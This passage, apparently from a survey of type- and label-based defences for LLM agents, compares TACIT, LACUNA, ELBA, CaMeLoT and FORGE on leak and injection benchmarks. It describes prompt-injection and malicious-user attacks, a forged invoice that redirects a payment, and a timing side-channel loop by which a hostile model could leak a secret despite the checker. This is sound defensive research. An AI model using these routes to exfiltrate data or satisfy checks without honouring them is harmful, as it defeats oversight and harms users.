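The function given to `map` also has to be written before the main model has any information about the contents. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), a follow-up by the same group, gets around this by letting that function call a trusted local model, which reads the contents and writes more code on the spot. The compiler checks the new code under the same restrictions. With the supplier's spreadsheet, the local model could detect that refunds appear as negative sales, write a suitable calculation and return a wrapped total. This is multi-shot execution on data that the main model never receives. However, the main model couldn't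 base its next step on the total unless someone unwrapped it.

### Leaks and task performance in TACIT

To test for leaks, Odersky and colleagues gave agents a software project with a directory of secrets. They combined 12 ordinary tasks with 10 injections, and added 11 requests in which the user asked for the secrets directly or posed as someone entitled to them. The table shows how many runs leaked a secret:

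| Model | Type of attack | Secrets wrapped | Secrets as plain text |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | injection | 0 of 120 | 0 of 120 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | malicious user | 0 of 11 | 2 of 11 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | injection | 0 of 120 | 3 of 120 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | malicious user | 0 of 11 | 8 of 11 |

The injections were a weak test of the wrapper because they rarely worked even without it. The malicious requests are better evidence, because MiniMax leaked secrets in most of them without the wrapper and in none with it. The wrapper didn't reduce the number of ordinary tasks completed. Claude completed 99.2 percent with it and 83.3 percent without it. The lower rate was partly because Claude ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about injections when the secrets were in plain text.

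Writing Scala did little or no harm to scores on other benchmarks. On τ²-bench, which simulates customer service for an airline and a shop, three models scored between 0.8 and 3.7 points higher when they wrote typed programs than when they called tools directly. On a set of software repairs, MiniMax's score fell from 43.3 to 41.7 percent. But the customer-service tools returned ordinary, unwrapped data, so the scores show that models can write typed Scala but don't measure how well they work when they can't read the results.

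AgentDojo is more informative on that point. In the TACIT version, tools that read emails, files, messages or web pages return wrapped values, so the planner never reads most of the planted text. One of 1,926 attacks succeeded, in the hotel-review case mentioned earlier. The percentage of tasks completed varied widely:

| Model | System | Banking | Workspace | Slack | Travel |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
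| Gemini 2.5 Pro | CaMeL | 52.8 | 53.8 | 48.6 | 1.4 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | TACIT | 56.9 | 50.5 | 40.0 | 64.3 |
| o4-mini-high | CaMeL | 62.5 | 81.4 | 68.6 | 74.3 |
| o4-mini-high | TACIT | 59.0 | 52.9 | 47.6 | 68.6 |

With o4-mini-high, TACIT's completion rate was 28 percentage points lower than the other system's on workspace tasks and 21 points lower on Slack tasks. Odersky and colleagues are therefore generous to TACIT when they describe the two systems as comparable.

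How often the compiler rejects a program depends on the model and the task. In TACIT's customer-service tests, at most 8 percent of programs needed another attempt. With LACUNA, the compiler rejected 22.4 percent of one model's programs for the shop and 89 percent of a weaker model's programs for a telecoms company. On τ²-bench, the stronger model solved 76 percent of tasks with LACUNA and 90 percent without it, though Zhao and colleagues call LACUNA's overall result on par with an ordinary agent's.

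### Language-based agent control

*Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) applies the same idea to integrity as well as secrecy. Its system, ELBA, uses Haskell, a language in which a program's type shows what effects it can have. A developer writes a policy by choosing the type the agent's program must have.

One example is an agent that compiles bibliographies and must not invent references. The function that writes to the bibliography accepts only values of type `Trusted Bib`, and only the function that fetches entries from DBLP, a computer-science database, can create such a value. The agent can sort and filter entries freely. If it writes a reference from memory, the result is a plain string, so the program doesn't compile. In a test of 100 tasks, an ordinary agent invented details in 19 of 1,002 references, while ELBA's agent did so in none of its 925.

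This would also block the copied account number in the Harlow Plumbing example if `send_money` accepted only an account type whose values came from the user's own records. The planner could still write `"70938214"`, but that string would have the wrong type.

An ELBA program can call the model again and pass it what the program has found. The compiler requires the new program to fit the type expected at that point, so it can't do anything the first program's type forbids. Zhou and colleagues prove a general version of this. Let a trace be a sequence of tool calls, and let $P$ be a property that the language guarantees for every ordinary program $e$ of type $t$:

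$$\vdash e : t \;\Rightarrow\; P(\text{traces}(e)).$$

Then $P$ also holds for programs that call agents, as long as each generated program passes the type checker before it runs. The proof replaces every agent call with an ordinary function that queries the model, checks the reply and runs it. Replies may contain further agent calls, so the proof starts with calls at the maximum depth, which return nothing, and works upwards. The resulting program is ordinary and has the same traces, so the original guarantee applies. The theorem guarantees only $P$, so if a type permits a harmful call, generated programs can make that call at every depth.

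ELBA handles information flow with LIO, the Haskell library whose current label works like a context label. The type checker ensures that every action goes through LIO, which checks the labels as the program runs. A program can also run a sub-agent under a separate label and get back a labelled result, much as LLMbda does with `fork`. Unlike a quarantined model, the sub-agent can use tools after reading untrusted text if its label allows them.

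Zhou and colleagues tested ELBA on AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks. With policies on and no attacks, it completed 8 to 10 tasks depending on the model, while CaMeL completed 4 to 6. The systems enforce different policies, so the labels alone may not explain the gap. ELBA also took about three times as long, because its agents call the model again as they get new information.

None of AgentDojo's attacks succeeded against any of the four models, even without policies. The researchers therefore built a harsher test, in which they replaced a sub-agent's instructions with the attacker's whenever it read an injection. They ran each of the 105 combinations of task and attack seven times:

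| Model | Attacks succeeding, no policies | Attacks succeeding, policies on | Tasks completed, no policies | Tasks completed, policies on |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 42.2% | 0% | 71.2% | 47.8% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 37.4% | 0% | 75.8% | 42.4% |
| GPT-5.4 | 15.5% | 0% | 75.9% | 46.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 26.5% | 0% | 67.2% | 40.0% |

The zeros exclude 29 runs that AgentDojo counted as attacks although the agent had only opened a harmless fixed address. These results are some of the best evidence on labels in multi-shot execution, because the agents read real data before writing more code and the result doesn't depend on a model recognising an injection. The policies lowered the task completion rate by 23 to 33 percentage points. Slack is only one small set of tasks, though.

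### Rules about the order of events

Types are less convenient for rules that span a whole program, such as requiring approval before an irreversible step. *CaMeLoT* checks such rules on CaMeL's plans before any tool runs. It first turns the plan into a finite-state machine, a map of the points the program can reach and the steps between them. This conversion ignores the conditions on branches and loops, so the check covers both sides of every branch and any number of loop repetitions.

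The rules use temporal logic, in which **A** means "on every path", **G** "at every point" and **U** "until". Two examples are:

$$\mathbf{AG}(\text{message sent} \Rightarrow \text{recipient trusted})$$

$$\mathbf{A}[\neg\,\text{computer isolated} \;\;\mathbf{U}\;\; \text{computer confirmed}]$$

The second rule forbids an agent that handles security alerts from disconnecting a computer from the network until the agent has confirmed that it is the right computer.

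A program called a model checker searches every path for a violation. Suppose a plan reads a channel's messages, has the quarantined model find Bob's address in them, and sends a message to that address. The model checker returns a counterexample, the sequence of steps leading to a message with an untrusted recipient. CaMeLoT turns this into a prompt containing the broken rule, the path and repair instructions. The planner then writes another plan, and the cycle repeats until a plan passes or the attempts run out.

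CaMeLoT and CaMeL made the same decision on 59 of the 75 AgentDojo tasks that remained after excluding 22 that failed under both systems. Most disagreements involved facts that become available only when the program runs, such as who can read a file. The comparison allowed repair only for unsupported code, so it doesn't show how often a counterexample leads to a working plan. In a separate test on security alerts, CaMeLoT caught all seven unsafe plans and a simplified CaMeL caught one, but the researchers had chosen rules that CaMeL can't easily express.

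These rules can also catch omissions, such as the comparison of account numbers that the planner skipped because of a forged invoice. A rule requiring that comparison before any payment would reject the new program. However, CaMeLoT applies its rules to a single plan. In a multi-shot agent, the comparison might happen in one program and the payment in the next, so the checker would need a record of past events. The checker also couldn't require every program to finish what an earlier one began, since a later program might finish it.

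### What a rejection can reveal

A compiler error or a counterexample goes back to the planner, so it needs a label like any other input. Let $p_k$ be the program, $\Gamma_k$ the types of the variables and functions saved from earlier programs, and $R$ the rules. A checker that looks at nothing else returns a verdict $v_k$ with the label

$$\lambda(v_k) = \lambda(p_k) \sqcup \lambda(\Gamma_k) \sqcup \lambda(R).$$

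The planner wrote the program, so $\lambda(p_k)$ is the planner's context label, $c_k$. If the saved types and the rules depend only on what the planner has already read, the feedback can't raise that label. CaMeLoT's counterexamples meet this condition, because the plan hasn't fetched any email when the model checker examines it. The errors in CaMeL's retry loop don't meet it, since they can arrive after a program has read secret or untrusted data.

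The same feedback is riskier if it reaches a model that didn't write the rejected code. In LACUNA, a call that runs out of attempts raises an exception containing the compiler's messages. Suppose a local model reads a secret contract and writes code that uses an undefined name, `AcmeTakeover`. The message "Not found: value AcmeTakeover" would reveal the deal if it reached the main planner. The system would have to keep such messages inside the wrapper.

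Errors that occur during a run are harder to contain. In its AgentDojo tests, TACIT hides any exception raised by a function inside `map`, so the agent receives no error and the user receives an empty result. That prevents a leak, but it also makes an honest mistake difficult to fix. It doesn't hide how long the function takes:

```
balance.map { b => while b > 500000 do () }
```

This function is pure, so it compiles, but it never finishes if the balance is above £500,000. An agent that notices the delay learns one bit about the balance. A hostile model in a TACIT session could repeat this with other thresholds, much as Garby and colleagues describe for CaMeL's retry loop. Odersky and colleagues exclude timing and termination from their guarantee.

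Some checkers also give feedback based on what the agent has already read. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) describes FORGE, which lets an agent read any file but blocks an email once both untrusted and sensitive data have entered the agent's context. FORGE then sends the agent a structured explanation. Attacks succeeded in none of five trials with this policy, and in all five when the agent had only a prompt telling it not to leak data. The explanation depends on the files in the agent's context, so it should carry their labels if another agent or a new conversation receives it.

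Feedback can also lead the planner to satisfy a rule without solving the problem. CaMeLoT treats constants as trusted, so a planner told that its recipient is untrusted could hard-code a made-up address, and the new plan would pass.

### Harmful choices among permitted actions

TACIT limits what an agent can do under the influence of untrusted text, but doesn't try to prevent that influence. The limits are only as tight as the permissions a developer grants. In LACUNA's AgentDojo tests, each agent had only the permissions its task needed, and 8 attacks still succeeded across the two models. Zhao and colleagues say their system doesn't block an attacker who persuades the model to misuse a permission it legitimately has.

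Permission to run other software can be especially broad, because the compiler can't check what happens outside Scala. Odersky and colleagues suggest restricting agents to specific safe commands, such as `sbt`, Scala's build tool. But `sbt` runs a project's build file as code. An agent that could edit that file and then run `sbt` would escape the type checker, so TACIT would need an operating-system sandbox around it.

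Stricter types limit an attacker's choice of account but don't remove it. Suppose `send_money` accepts only accounts from the user's records, which include both Harlow Plumbing and a builder called Bexley. An attacker forges an invoice with a note that Bexley now collects Harlow's payments, and the planner reads it as plain text. The planner then looks up Bexley's account and writes a program to pay it £1,240. The program compiles because the account has the right type, but the money goes to the wrong firm. To prevent this, the system would also need to mark the planner's decision as untrusted, as a context label does.
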